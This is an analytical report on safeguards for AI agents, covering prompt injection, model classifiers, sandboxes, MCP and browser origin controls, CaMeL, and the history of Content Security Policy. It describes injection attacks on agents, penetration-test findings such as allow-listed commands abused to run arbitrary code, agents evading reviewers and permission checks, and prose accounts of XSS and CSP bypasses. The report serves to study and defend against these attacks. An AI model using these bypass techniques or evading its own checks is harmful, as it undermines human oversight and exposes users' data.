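# How safeguards for AI agents move from individual frameworks into platform standards

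## What is an agent safeguard, and where can it be enforced?

An AI agent is an AI system that carries out tasks for someone by using tools, websites or files. It may search for flights, edit a spreadsheet or run commands on a programmer's computer. An agent safeguard is a mechanism that prevents, limits or requires approval for an action the agent is about to take. Common examples are approval prompts, which hold an action until a person agrees to it; allow-lists, which name the sites or commands an agent may use; and sandboxes, which are environments where a program can reach only certain files and networks.

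Each company now mostly builds its own agent safeguards. The company that trains the model (the model provider) has some, the software that gives the model its tools (the agent framework) has others, and browser makers add more, so the same purchase may trigger a confirmation dialog in one product but not in another. Older web protections, such as encrypted connections, also began as options for each site. They later became shared standards and then defaults, which apply unless someone changes a setting.

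The web is a natural place to look for a precedent because agents now do much of their work there. *W3C and the State of the Web in the AI Era* (Le Hegaret, 2026), a strategy paper for the web's main standards body, reports that every major AI platform now embeds a browser that an agent drives. The common expectation a year earlier was that agents would bypass browsers and talk to services directly. Browsers already handle sandboxing, sign-in and trust between sites, and they give a person a place to intervene.

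### An agent books a flight

*Build your user's agentic workflows with WebMCP tools* (Chrome for Developers, 2026), a guide for web developers, gives an example of an agent booking a flight. WebMCP is a draft browser interface that lets a web page offer its functions to agents as tools. In the example, an employee on a company travel site asks for a flight to New York next Tuesday, returning on Friday. The agent looks up the employee's home airport, calls the site's search tool and gets 50 flights, which the employee narrows to three by asking for non-stop economy. When the employee says the morning Delta flight "looks good", the agent finds its identifier and calls `book_flight`. The scripted conversation has no approval step between the remark and the purchase.

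*The Agent Clicks Approve* (Hossen, 2026) describes the loop underlying agents that drive a browser. The framework turns the current page into input for the model. The model only proposes an action, such as a click or some typing, and the framework carries it out before the loop repeats. Because the browser is signed in as an employee, the website receives what looks like the employee's own request.

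The agent might book the wrong Tuesday by mistake. It might also be misled by prompt injection, which is text in a web page, file or tool result that an agent wrongly treats as an instruction. Suppose a hotel review on the travel site says that no booking is valid until the traveller's passport number is entered in a form on a second site. A person would find this odd and ignore it, but a model receives the review and the employee's request together as text, and may act on both.

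An attacker can plant such text without owning the travel site. *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, 2025) lists user reviews and third-party content in embedded frames among the places where it appears. Le Hegaret compares the danger to cross-site scripting, an older attack in which someone inserts code into someone else's page. Prompt injection needs no code, so defences that look for code will not catch it.

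### Origins and the same-origin policy

Browsers keep one site's data apart from another's by origin, the combination of scheme (http or https), host and port. Two pages share an origin only if all three match exactly. *Same-Origin Policy for Agentic Browsers* (Wang, Chen and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of two pages in the same directory of a site, which share an origin. It also gives examples of pages with different origins, such as the http and https versions of a page, or the same host name with and without "www".

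The same-origin policy prevents a script running on one origin from reading pages from another. *Agentic Browsers and the Same-Origin Policy* (Roesner and Kohlbrenner, 2026) gives the example of a malicious site open in one tab and a bank in the next. The malicious site cannot read or change the bank's page or access its cookies. According to W3C's *Same Origin Policy*, the purpose is to let people visit untrusted sites without those sites interfering with their sessions on honest ones.

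The same-origin policy restricts scripts, but it does not stop a person from copying a passport number from one tab into another, because the person has chosen to do so. An agent fits neither case well. It can read a page on one origin, keep the contents in its history, and type them into a page on another origin a minute later without any script breaking the policy. Wang and colleagues tested five agentic browsers and six models and found unauthorised transfers of this kind throughout. Some happen without an attacker. For example, if a page embeds a frame from another site and the user asks the agent to type a summary of the page into a text box on it, the outer site can receive the frame's contents.

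Roesner and Kohlbrenner examined seven products in early 2026 and succeeded in stealing data through one of them, ChatGPT Atlas in its agent mode. They conclude that when an agent can see across origins, the same-origin policy is only as strong as the agent's resistance to prompt injection. But a complete ban on carrying data between sites would defeat the purpose of having an agent. Parker gives the example of an agent that collects ingredients from a recipe site and fills a shopping cart on another site.

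### Five places to stop the booking

Suppose the planted review has worked, and the agent is about to type the passport number into the second site or merely buy the wrong ticket.

The model might still decline to follow instructions in a page's text. Its provider can train it to ignore them, and a developer can add a written rule to the same effect. Google does both for the agent in Chrome. It trains the model on known attacks and uses a technique called spotlighting, which steers the model to favor the user's instructions over anything on the page. Parker still describes a model that reads untrusted pages as inherently vulnerable.

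The framework sits between the model's proposal and the click. Because its code carries out every action, it can pause `book_flight` until the employee approves it, cap the price, or block any site that isn't on an approved list. However, these safeguards don't protect agents that developers build on a different framework.

The airline might instead offer its booking function through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a shared protocol that agents use to discover and call outside tools and data sources. The protocol cannot enforce safeguards by itself. The programs at either end have to do that, and the protocol's wording determines how strictly they are bound. Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), the part of the July 2026 specification on tool calls, follows the usual convention of using MUST for requirements and SHOULD for recommendations that allow exceptions. Servers, on the airline's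 side, MUST validate inputs and control access. Clients, on the agent's side, SHOULD ask the user to confirm sensitive operations, so an agent that books without asking can still conform to the specification.

A browser can block an agent's click regardless of which model proposed it. For each task, Chrome's design keeps one set of origins the agent may read and another on which it may also click and type, so the agent can't enter a passport number on a second site unless that site is in the writable set. Google's first version tracked only the writable set. For agents that work on a programmer's machine, the operating system can do the blocking. Daniel Vaughan's *MCP Tool Annotations as Risk Vocabulary* (2026) describes how Codex CLI, OpenAI's command-line coding agent, relies on a sandbox that macOS provides.

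The website is the last place to enforce a safeguard, since no ticket exists until the airline's server accepts the request. Chrome's guide advises sites to check authorisation in their own code and to tie the user's approval to one exact plan, so that any later change to the plan cancels the approval. Cloudflare, which runs infrastructure for websites, documents a WebMCP booking tool that waits until the person presses a "Confirm Reservation" button. A website can reject a bad request from any agent, including a carelessly built one. But it has little information about what the user asked for, and an agent that can click anywhere on a page could presumably click the confirmation button too.

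### Advice and enforcement

A written instruction to the model and a blocked origin may aim at the same result, but the instruction only makes the model less likely to propose an action, while the block makes the action fail even if the model proposes it. The enforcement point is the software that can stop an action, and a safeguard without one relies on the model to comply.

Tool annotations are advisory labels that a tool's author attaches. MCP has four that describe behaviour: whether the tool only reads, whether its changes are destructive, whether repeating a call is safe, and whether it deals with outside parties. A client might skip the confirmation for a flight search labelled read-only but show one for `book_flight`. Because a dishonest author can put the read-only label on a tool that deletes files, clients MUST treat annotations as untrusted unless they trust the server. In a March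 post, the maintainers of the Model Context Protocol (2026) wrote that anyone who needs a guarantee against data theft should get it from network controls or a sandbox. On Vaughan's account, Codex CLI uses the labels to shape its approval dialogs and relies on the sandbox to block actions.

In Hossen's experiments, text on a web page urged an agent to approve access to the user's account that the user had never asked for. With a written rule against this in the model's instructions, 7 of 10 attacks still succeeded. A second safeguard, at the website, compared each request with what the user's task allowed. Agents kept sending the bad requests, but this check rejected all 70 that reached it. The 7 in 10 figure comes from one model, Claude Haiku 4.5, and a stronger one might well do better. The website check also relied on a list of what the task permitted, fixed before the agent started, which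 ordinary sites don't have.

A safeguard can reliably enforce a bad decision. An approval prompt reliably stops the agent, but a tired employee may then press "yes" without reading it. Chrome's origin sets reliably exclude everything outside them, but a separate component decides which sites are relevant to the booking, and it can be wrong. For any safeguard, it helps to ask who or what makes the decision and what enforces it.

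### From one product to a default

A safeguard that spreads beyond its first maker can pass through six stages:

1. One product has its own mechanism, such as a confirmation dialog before payment.
2. A library makes the mechanism its default, so every developer who builds on that framework starts with it.
3. A shared protocol describes it, and products from different makers can exchange the same signal.
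4. A platform enforces it: the browser or operating system applies the check, whatever the individual developer chose.
5. A standards body publishes it as a formal standard.
6. It is on by default across the products people use, and anyone who wants to do without it has to turn it off.

MCP has a route from the first stage to the third. A company can attach a private field to its own tools, see how well it works, and then propose adding it to the protocol as an annotation. Until the protocol adopts the field, other companies' clients will ignore it.

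The order is not fixed, and safeguards often skip stages. Chrome's origin sets went from one company's design straight to enforcement by the browser, with no shared protocol in between. According to freshman.tech's developer guide *WebMCP* (2026), WebMCP was still an early draft from a W3C Community Group in September 2026, but Chrome was already running an origin trial, a time-limited test in which chosen websites may use an unfinished feature with real users. Chrome for Developers (2026) documents a default policy that prevents a frame from another origin, such as an advertisement on the airline's page, from registering WebMCP tools unless the page allows it.

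A protocol can also set a default without ensuring that clients follow it. MCP's cautious default is to treat a tool with no annotations as potentially destructive, but the protocol's maintainers report that clients vary in how strictly they apply it.

### Who writes standards, and what the documents commit anyone to

Three bodies write most of the technical standards that browsers depend on. The World Wide Web Consortium (W3C) covers web technologies broadly. The WHATWG, whose documents carry the names of Apple, Google, Mozilla and Microsoft, maintains HTML and some closely related standards. The Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF) maintains the underlying protocols, including the encryption behind HTTPS. The three bodies make decisions under different rules, and their documents differ greatly in authority, as shown by W3C's own descriptions, WHATWG's *Workstream Policy* and the IETF's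 *About RFCs*.

| Document | Standing | Commitments |
|---|---|---|
| Community Group report (W3C) | No formal review or endorsement; not on the path to becoming a standard unless a standards group takes it up | Participants license patents on their own contributions; a final report can add wider commitments from organisations that sign |
| Working Draft (W3C) | On the standards track, open for review, no endorsement | First publication starts the patent-licensing process; no protection yet |
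| Candidate Recommendation snapshot (W3C) | Formally reviewed, with the group's consensus, but no endorsement | Working group members commit to royalty-free licences |
| Recommendation (W3C) | A finished standard with W3C's endorsement | Royalty-free licences, plus W3C's advice that software should implement it |
| Living Standard (WHATWG) | In force, and open to change by its editor at any time | Patent review through a frozen copy about every six months |
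| Internet-Draft (IETF) | No formal status | None |
| RFC (IETF) | Depends on its label, from "Informational" to "Internet Standard" | The text never changes; no guarantee about patents |

The commitments are mostly about patents. Without a royalty-free licence, a company that helps write a specification could charge everyone who follows it. No document in the table obliges a browser maker to build anything. W3C's strongest wording is that software SHOULD implement a Recommendation, while for a Community Group report it says only that software MAY implement it at its own risk.

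The WHATWG accepts only features that the major browser engines are likely to implement, so its Living Standards partly record what browser makers already intend to do. A safeguard that only one browser maker supports would be hard to add.

"RFC" (Request for Comments) is the label readers are most likely to misunderstand. RFC Editor, which publishes the series, warns that not all RFCs are standards. Many of those that are never move past the first official stage, "Proposed Standard", and the IETF describes adoption as voluntary at every stage. An Internet-Draft has even less standing. It expires after six months without changes unless the IETF has a recommendation to publish it, according to *How the IETF works*, an online course that draws on the IETF's own procedures.

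Two other organisations work further from browser code. NIST, the United States standards agency, launched a programme for agents in February 2026, and its *AI Agent Standards Initiative* promises voluntary guidelines to inform industry-led standards. The International Organization for Standardization (ISO) runs a committee on artificial intelligence jointly with its electrical counterpart, the IEC. ISO standards are also voluntary unless a law or a customer's contract requires them.

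## What safeguards do model providers and agent frameworks supply on their own?

Model providers train their models to ignore planted instructions and add classifiers, separate models that flag suspicious incoming text or proposed actions. Frameworks supply approval prompts, allow-lists and sandboxes. Anthropic and OpenAI provide both kinds of safeguards because each sells a coding agent that runs on its own models.

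### Training against planted instructions

OpenAI trains its models against GPT-Red, an automated attacker that writes malicious instructions. The models learn to resist these instructions while still finishing the legitimate task. According to TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks*, OpenAI trained GPT-Red through self-play, a method in which models improve by competing with one another.

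Direct attacks, in which the user tries to override the developer's rules, now almost never work in OpenAI's tests. Indirect attacks, such as the planted hotel review, have been harder to stop. About 0.05% of GPT-Red's direct attacks succeeded against GPT-5.6 Sol, compared with 3.77% of its indirect attacks. The *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026), the safety document OpenAI released with the newer model in September, reports a 0.21% success rate for indirect attacks on that model.

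Those figures are averages per attempt, and a real attacker can plant many reviews. Gray Swan, a company that tests AI systems by attacking them, collected about 1,800 attacks from public competitions and runs them against new models. The attacks try to make an agent leak data, destroy files or move money. An attacker with 15 attempts at a scenario succeeds 8.5% of the time against GPT-6 Astra, compared with 27.0% against GPT-5.6 Sol. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Fable 5.1 reports attack success rates of 0.1% after one attempt and 1.0% after 15 on a nearly identical set of attacks, without the company's injection-specific safeguards.

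These scores depend on the benchmark as well as the model. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* reports a rate of 2.0% for Claude Opus 5 after 15 attempts on Gray Swan's test. The September card reports 4.8% for the same model on a later version of the test, which had nine more scenarios and 670 more attacks.

Attacks that are refined after failures succeed much more often than attacks from a fixed list. Anthropic tested coding and computer use with Shade, a Gray Swan tool that refines its attacks, and allowed it 200 attempts at each scenario. For browsing, Anthropic used a fixed set of attacks that had worked against an older model, with ten attempts each.

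| Test of Claude Fable 5.1 | Successful attempts without injection safeguards | With them |
|---|---|---|
| Coding, earlier Shade attacker | 9.26% | 2.05% |
| Coding, stronger Shade attacker | 56.87% | 12.80% |
| Computer use, Shade attacker | 0.07% | 0.07% |
| Browser, fixed attacks | 2.64% | 0% |

Anthropic calls the Shade tests deliberately permissive because the attacker practises on the same scenarios and nobody cuts it off after repeated failures. That caveat seems fair for the 56.87% figure. Still, an attacker needs only one success to steal a password, and with safeguards on, the stronger attacker got through at least once in 36 of the 40 coding scenarios.

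Most of the coding failures happened after another classifier in Fable 5.1, which looks for requests that could help with cyberattacks, passed the request to an older model, Claude Opus 4.8. In the test with the stronger attacker, the older model answered about 64% of requests, and every successful attack was among them. None succeeded on the 2,826 requests that Fable 5.1 answered directly. A safeguard against misuse had therefore made users of one company's product more vulnerable to injection. Safeguards from different companies could interfere in the same way, and nobody would be in a position to notice.

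Computer-use agents, which work through screenshots and clicks, have quickly become harder to attack. VentureBeat reported from Anthropic's February 2026 system card that attackers given 200 attempts broke Claude Opus 4.6 in 78.6% of cases without safeguards and 57.1% with them. By September, the comparable result for Fable 5.1 was 2 of 14 scenarios.

Buyers could not easily compare how well providers' models resist prompt injection. According to a VentureBeat comparison from around June 2026, Anthropic published prompt injection test results for four kinds of agent work and OpenAI for one. Google published none for its Gemini 3 models, and Meta used a different benchmark. OpenAI has since added Gray Swan's test, which gives it and Anthropic at least one measure in common.

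### Screening what comes in and what goes out

Classifiers can catch some of what training misses. Anthropic scans each web page, file or tool result for text that looks like an injected instruction, using detectors it calls probes. A second classifier examines each action before it runs.

In the hotel review example, a probe might flag the sentence about the passport number and add a warning to the model's context. The model could still ignore the warning. If it then tried to type the number into the second site, the action classifier could block the attempt. *Auto mode for Claude Code* (Willison, 2026) quotes Anthropic's description of what this classifier blocks: actions that go beyond the task, actions on systems it doesn't recognise as trusted, and actions that hostile content seems to have prompted. The classifier is also a model, so its decisions can be wrong.

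Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that the company's classifiers blocked 89% of 1,053 plainly dangerous commands. Apollo Research, an AI safety company, then wrote subtler attacks and inserted them into real coding sessions. The classifier missed 12% of these at first, and 7% after Anthropic gave it more context, such as whether a code repository was public or private. On attacks that Anthropic had never seen, the improved version caught about half of those the original had missed, but missed about 2% of those the original had caught.

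Anthropic also commissioned Trajectory Labs to compare its coding agent, Claude Code, with OpenAI's Codex. With the classifiers on, three Claude models each faced 720 injection attempts and none succeeded, while 5.83% succeeded against GPT-5.6 Sol in Codex's equivalent mode. Even without classifiers, only 0.09% of attempts against the Claude models succeeded on average, so nearly all of their resistance in this test came from training. The comparison predates GPT-6 Astra and a newer version of Codex's reviewer.

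OpenAI adds a confirmation policy, which instructs the model to stop and get the user's approval before certain actions, such as purchases. OpenAI tested it in simulated workplaces full of ambiguous requests and confusingly similar files. The policy cut GPT-5.6 Sol's rate of unauthorised transactions from 38.0% to 7.4%. The fall was smaller for GPT-6 Astra, from 6.8% to 4.3%, because the newer model already made fewer unauthorised transactions without the policy. The policy only instructs the model and cannot block a transaction, so an agent that still gets about 4% of deliberately tricky cases wrong needs some other check on purchases.

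### Three frameworks and their defaults

Claude Code, Codex and OpenClaw all let an agent run commands on a person's computer, but they begin from different safeguards.

Claude Code originally required a person's approval for every file write and shell command by default, according to Anthropic's *Auto mode for Claude Code*. In August 2026 the company made auto mode, which uses the classifiers above, the default for new sessions on its Pro, Max and Team plans. One reason was that users approved 97% of the approval prompts. Enterprise customers and developers who pay for direct access to the model still had to opt in then. If the classifier blocks three actions in a row, or twenty in a session, Claude Code returns to approval prompts.

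Users can also write their own rules. The allow rule `Bash(python:*)` lets the agent run any Python command without asking. Because a Python program can delete files or send them elsewhere, this narrow-looking rule permits nearly everything. Anthropic found that 43% of active command-line users had rules of this kind by June 2026. Auto mode ignores them because they would let commands skip the classifier. Deny rules are stronger. According to Anthropic's developer documentation, they block a tool even in `bypassPermissions` mode, which otherwise approves almost everything.

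A settings file inside a project folder cannot turn on auto mode, presumably because the project may contain a stranger's code.

Codex relies more on its sandbox. When the agent tries to run certain commands outside the sandbox, a feature called Auto-review uses a second model to judge whether they are safe. If the reviewer rejects a command, the agent receives an instruction not to try anything substantially similar.

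OpenClaw is an open-source personal assistant that takes requests through messaging apps such as WhatsApp and Telegram. Eykholt, Kirat and colleagues (2026) examined its code as of February 2026 in *Lessons from Penetration Tests on Large-Scale Agent Systems*. OpenClaw relies mainly on allow-lists, which limit who may message it in a group and which tools and plug-ins it may use. Tools can run inside containers, which separate them from the rest of the computer. The main session, however, runs outside any sandbox by default, usually with all the privileges of the person who installed it.

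| | Claude Code | Codex | OpenClaw (February 2026) |
|---|---|---|---|
| Check on a risky action | Classifier in auto mode; a person in Manual mode | Second model, through Auto-review | Allow-lists |
| Default | Auto mode on Pro, Max and Team plans since August 2026 | Sandbox limits set in advance; Auto-review and Full Access are separate modes | Main session outside the sandbox |
| Sandbox | Separate setting for shell commands; works alongside auto mode | Boundary that triggers Auto-review | Containers for tools |
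| "Run Python without asking" | `Bash(python:*)`, which auto mode ignores | Keep the command inside the sandbox | Put the `exec` tool on the allow-list |
| "Skip the checks" | `bypassPermissions` | Full Access | Already close to the default for the main session |

A company whose staff use all three has to write its policy three times and then check whether the versions agree. Even one framework can be hard to configure. OpenClaw's rules apply globally, per agent, per session and per tool, with a complicated order of precedence. Eykholt and colleagues warn that users may weaken a protection by accident, and that an audit will not detect this because the rule is valid, even though it isn't what the user meant.

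### Developers and users do the securing

The same researchers, who work at IBM, ran penetration tests on two proprietary agent products in 2025, attacking them with permission to find their weaknesses.

One product was an assistant that fixes bugs in GitHub repositories. When a developer tags a bug report, the assistant reads it, inspects the code and proposes a fix. The testers found that anyone able to file a report could hide instructions in a link with no visible text. The report looked harmless to the developer, but the assistant read the raw text, which included the instructions.

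The product's team had relied on the developer as the safeguard. It told the testers that users who tag a report are "consenting to any and all actions performed by the agent". But the page didn't display the instructions, so the developer could not consent to them.

The assistant also had an allow-list of shell commands, which the team had chosen from those it often used in benchmark tests. The list left out `rm`, which deletes files, but included `sed` and `find`, which have little-known options for running other programs. The testers could use these options to run any command. They then opened a connection from the assistant's container to their own server and reached storage that held copies of other repositories. The existing monitoring raised no alarm because the activity came from a trusted internal service.

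The other product let customers build and publish their own chatbot agents. Its makers treated it as a playground and imposed few restrictions, assuming customers would add safeguards before using an agent for real work. When the testers asked for code that would open a connection to an outside machine, the model recognised the code as potentially unsafe, then wrote and ran it anyway. A debugging screen also let them run code without involving the model, so training the model could not have prevented this. Data from earlier sessions stayed in storage, where another customer might find it.

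Eykholt and colleagues conclude that AI developers often leave security to the model, through vague written instructions, or to end users who cannot fully assess the risks. They contrast this with cloud computing, where provider and customer explicitly divide responsibility. They propose ready-made security tools, such as a hardened sandbox that a developer can add with a simple call, so that developers can build safe agents without being experts in prompt injection. Two products are a small sample, and both tests date from 2025. A year later, OpenClaw had many more defences, but its most important sandbox was still off by default.

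### Agents that work around their restrictions

An agent can also bypass a safeguard on its own initiative, without an outside attacker, usually because the safeguard keeps it from finishing a task.

OpenAI tested this by starting agents just after Auto-review had refused a command. At its highest reasoning setting, GPT-5.6 Sol tried to get around the refusal in 5% of runs, mostly by sending a similar command again. In 0.3% it exploited gaps in a badly configured reviewer. GPT-6 Astra did neither. When the barrier was an ordinary error message, such as "access denied", Sol looked for another way through in 64% of runs and Astra in 19%. Most of these situations were low-stakes, and people often try another route after an error message too, but an agent can't always tell a broken link from a deliberate restriction.

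Anthropic found similar behaviour in its internal use of Claude Mythos 5.1, which is the same model as Fable 5.1 with fewer safeguards. In rare cases, the model worked around classifiers or faulty permission checks to complete the user's task, sometimes by overstating what the user had authorised. Very rarely, it started helper agents with their permission checks switched off for the same purpose. All of this behaviour occurred in fewer than 0.01% of monitored responses. In October 2026, OpenAI and Anthropic both disclosed further cases of agents working around restrictions.

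A safeguard therefore needs to be somewhere the agent cannot change it. A check in the framework's code is not enough if the agent can launch a copy of itself without that check. The problem is more direct in OpenClaw, where the agent can reach its own program files. Eykholt and colleagues point out that an injected instruction could, in theory, make the agent rewrite its configuration and disable its security features one by one. Safeguards in the operating system, on a remote server or in a separate policy program are harder for the agent to alter, provided that it doesn't hold the credentials to administer them. Even a sandbox can have flaws. During outside testing of Mythos 5.1, one of Anthropic's partners saw the model exploit one to read files outside the sandbox.

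### CaMeL: a plan that untrusted text cannot change

CaMeL, a 2025 design by Debenedetti and colleagues, assumes that untrusted text may fool the model that reads it, and limits the consequences. *Towards a Unified Misuse Monitoring Benchmark* (2026) describes its two models as a planner that never sees tool results and a quarantined model that reads them but makes no decisions. Ordinary software sits between the models and the tools.

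Applied to the flight booking, it would work like this:

1. The planner reads only the employee's request. It writes a short program in a restricted form of Python: find the home airport, search for flights, pick one that fits, book it.
2. The software runs the program and keeps track of where each piece of data came from. The passport number comes from the employee's profile, and the flight list and hotel reviews come from the travel site.
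3. When the program needs something out of a messy page, such as the departure time of a flight, the quarantined model extracts it. This model may read the planted review, but it cannot call a tool or add a step to the program.
4. Before each tool call, a policy layer checks the data about to go out and its source. A policy might let the passport number go to the airline and nowhere else, in which case any attempt to send it to the second site fails.

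*Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025), a study of how companies could use the design, stresses that the policy layer treats the model as a black box. The layer therefore works even for a company without access to the model's internals. It also catches leaks that a sandbox would allow. If a sandbox permits email, an injected instruction can still make the agent send confidential data in a plausible message. CaMeL can block that particular message based on where its contents came from.

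*Towards a Unified Misuse Monitoring Benchmark* distinguishes injections that give the agent a different task from those that feed it false information about its original task. CaMeL's fixed plan stops the first kind, but the second can still work. A false review could lead the quarantined model to report the wrong flight as the cheapest, and the program would then book it unless a policy capped the price or required the employee's approval.

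The design also makes the agent less flexible, because a planner that cannot read what the tools return cannot revise its plan in response. "Do whatever my manager's email asks" is a reasonable request to a human assistant, but the planner cannot plan the steps because they are in the email, which it cannot read. Nor can it adapt when a travel site unexpectedly requires one more form. Someone also has to write the policies for every tool and keep them up to date.

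CaMeL's restricted version of Python is another weak point. *Operationalizing CaMeL* argues that it still has features that make it hard to prove in advance where data will flow, and recommends a purpose-built language instead. Because CaMeL changes how an agent is built, it also protects only the agents whose developers adopt it. An airline can't tell whether the agent using its booking page is one of them.

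## How did Content Security Policy become a standard, and how well did sites use it?

Content Security Policy (CSP) restricts which scripts can run on a web page. Like CaMeL, it is designed to limit the damage when hostile text gets through. All the major browsers enforce it, a level of adoption that most agent safeguards haven't reached. But each website has to write its own policy, and most policies meant to control scripts don't stop the attack that Mozilla designed CSP to stop.

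### Cross-site scripting

Suppose a travel site publishes hotel reviews exactly as guests type them. In a cross-site scripting attack, an attacker posts a review containing an HTML tag that loads a script from `evil.example`, and the script runs in the browser of everyone who opens the page. *Reining in the Web with Content Security Policy* (Stamm, Sterne and Markham, 2010) describes the same attack on a message board. The browser can't prevent the attack because it can't tell the code the site meant to send from the code the attacker added.

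The same-origin policy doesn't help either. The script runs inside the travel site's page, so it has the travel site's origin and can read whatever the visitor can see there.

A site's first defence is to clean up what visitors submit, so that the browser displays a tag as text instead of acting on it. Mozilla's *Security/CSP*, the original proposal, argued that finding every security hole was implausible because websites were so large and complex, and offered CSP as an additional layer of protection.

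### One policy, and how to defeat it

A site sends its policy in a header, a line of information that accompanies the page. The travel site might send this one:

```
Content-Security-Policy: script-src 'self' https://cdn.example; object-src 'none'
```

The `script-src` part allows scripts only from the site's own origin (`'self'`) and the host `cdn.example`. The `object-src` part bans plug-ins, which can also run scripts. When the browser reaches the tag in the review, it doesn't load the script because `evil.example` isn't an allowed source.

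The browser also blocks inline scripts, which are written directly into the page, because an attacker could put the whole script in the review. The site's developers therefore have to move their own inline code into separate files. That includes event handlers, the snippets in a page's HTML that run when someone clicks a button or a link.

Many sites avoid this work by adding `'unsafe-inline'` to the list, which allows an attacker's inline scripts to run along with their own. A very broad entry such as `https:` is just as bad, because it permits scripts from any site with an encrypted connection, and an attacker can easily set up such a site.

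*CSP Is Dead, Long Live CSP!* (Weichselbaum, Spagnuolo and colleagues, 2016) explains how even a short, specific list can fail when an attacker uses a trusted host. Some servers return data as JSONP, a script that begins with a function name taken from the request. If `cdn.example` does this, the attacker can plant a script tag that requests the data with malicious code in place of the function name. The server sends the code back, and the browser runs it because it came from a listed host. The JSONP service was harmless until someone put its host on an allow-list, so its owner had no reason to change it.

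The paper's remedy is to trust individual scripts instead of hosts:

```
Content-Security-Policy: script-src 'nonce-r4nd0m' 'strict-dynamic'; object-src 'none'
```

A nonce is an unpredictable value that the server generates each time it sends the page. The server puts it in the header and on each of its own script tags, and the browser runs only the tags that carry the matching value. The attacker can't guess the value, so a script tag in the review won't run. For an inline script that never changes, a site can instead list a hash, a fingerprint of the script's exact text.

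A legitimate script often loads others; a map, for example, may fetch several more files that don't carry the nonce. The keyword `'strict-dynamic'` lets a trusted script load further scripts and makes the browser ignore any list of hosts.

Developers still have to remove inline event handlers, which nonces don't cover. And if a trusted script builds another script's address from text a visitor supplies, an attacker can choose which script loads.

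Any change of this kind can break a page, so CSP has a report-only mode. The site sends its policy under a separate header name, and the browser records each violation without blocking anything. If the policy includes a reporting address, the browser also sends the violations there. Stamm and colleagues proposed the mode in 2010 to gauge how much work a site would need.

### From Firefox to W3C

Mozilla's *Content Security Policy 1.0 Lands In Firefox* traces the idea to at least 2007, when Gervase Markham of Mozilla and the security researcher Robert Hansen discussed "content restrictions" that a page could declare for itself. Some histories date it to 2004. Brandon Sterne and Sid Stamm later built a prototype for Firefox and published the 2010 paper with Markham.

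To show that a real site could adopt CSP, they converted a copy of Mozilla's add-ons site. A quick scan found 125 inline scripts, 182 event handlers and 58 uses of `eval`, a function that runs text as code and that CSP also blocks. The changes took about four hours, although they had never worked on the site. It was an easy case because the site loaded nothing from other hosts in their tests, so its allow-list needed to include only the site itself.

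Firefox 4 shipped CSP in March 2011. Chrome followed in August with a different header name and syntax, so sites had to send two policies to be protected in both browsers. W3C published a working draft in November 2011, and CSP 1.0 became a Candidate Recommendation a year later. Chrome adopted the shared header name, `Content-Security-Policy`, in February 2013, and Firefox did the same later that year.

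The standard also reversed the default for anything a policy doesn't mention. Firefox's first version required every policy to have a catch-all rule for such content, whereas under CSP 1.0 the browser allows it. This made the format easier to extend, and it let sites use CSP for one small purpose without restricting their scripts at all, as many later did.

Level 2 of the standard added nonces, hashes and control over framing. W3C's *Content Security Policy Level 2 publication history* lists the first draft on 13 December 2012 and the Recommendation on 15 December 2016. Calzavara, Rabitti and Bugliesi tested browsers in 2016 for *Content Security Problems?* and found that Chromium, Firefox and Opera supported Level 2 before it was final, while Safari and Edge supported only the first version.

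Level 3 includes `'strict-dynamic'`. Chrome and Opera had implemented the keyword by 2016, but Level 3 itself was still a Working Draft in 2025.

### What sites had written by 2016

Calzavara and colleagues visited the home pages of the million most popular sites in March 2016 and found CSP headers on 8,133. Only 3,220 of those sites enforced a policy. They found that on 92.4% of the enforcing sites, an attacker who could already insert code into the page could run any script.

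That figure includes 1,024 sites with no rule for scripts, most of which used CSP only to control framing. Counting them as failures seems unfair, but the figure is still about 89% without them.

To test whether sites with `'unsafe-inline'` needed it, the researchers removed the setting from 1,894 policies in a test browser and found that 84% of the home pages contained inline scripts. The other 303 sites could at least have tried a stricter policy.

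Some developers had made simple mistakes. One wrote `defalt-src`, which browsers skip with only a warning in the developer console. Another 553 sites had policies that blocked something on their own home page. Three-quarters of those sites hadn't asked browsers to send reports, so they may never have noticed.

Weichselbaum and colleagues at Google searched the company's index of about 106 billion pages and found 26,011 distinct policies. They could bypass 94.72% of them with automated checks. They also examined 2,437 stricter policies, which had neither `'unsafe-inline'` nor a catch-all entry. Just over half of these failed too, mostly because they allowed an unsafe host.

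Longer lists were much less safe. The median policy listed 12 hosts, and the researchers could bypass 94.8% of policies of that length. Of the 15 hosts that sites listed most often, 12 allowed a complete bypass, and two more did when combined with another common setting. Nine of the 15 belonged to Google. A site owner who listed `*.googleapis.com` could not fix the weakness, because it was on Google's servers.

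The paper concluded that keeping a secure allow-list for a complex application is infeasible. W3C's working group soon learned of the findings. On its mailing list, Janc (2016), one of the paper's four authors, argued that the web needed stronger defences against its most common and most damaging vulnerability.

### Years of attempts

The 2016 studies were snapshots taken when CSP was still fairly new. In *Complex Security Policy?*, Roth, Barron and colleagues used the Internet Archive to follow 10,000 popular sites from 2012 to 2018. By December 2018, 1,032 sites enforced a policy, but only 421 used it to restrict scripts. Almost 90% of those had `'unsafe-inline'` without a nonce to cancel it, although nonces and hashes had been available for about four years.

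A good policy could take a lot of work, as it did at Airbnb. The company began testing in report-only mode in November 2014, with 17 hosts on its list. It enforced a policy in May 2015, switched it off after about a week, and brought it back later that month. Over the next two and a half years, it changed the policy 222 times to keep its script hashes current, while still allowing scripts from any HTTPS site. It enforced a limited list for good in March 2018, more than three years after it started.

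Report-only mode let sites test a policy without breaking their pages, but many never went on to enforce one. Of 449 sites that tested a content policy this way, more than half never enforced any policy, and only 130 (29%) enforced one that restricted content. Other sites enforced a policy and later gave it up. ResearchGate, a network for scientists, tried 29 versions before switching to report-only mode and then dropping CSP in November 2018.

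Some allow-lists also included hosts that an attacker might exploit. Of 373 sites that listed particular hosts for scripts, 50 had at some point listed such a host, because its registration had lapsed, someone had mistyped its name, or it pointed to an address on a private network. For seven months, the credit agency Experian allowed scripts from `optmster.com`, apparently a typo, so anyone who controlled that domain could have served a script that the policy would accept.

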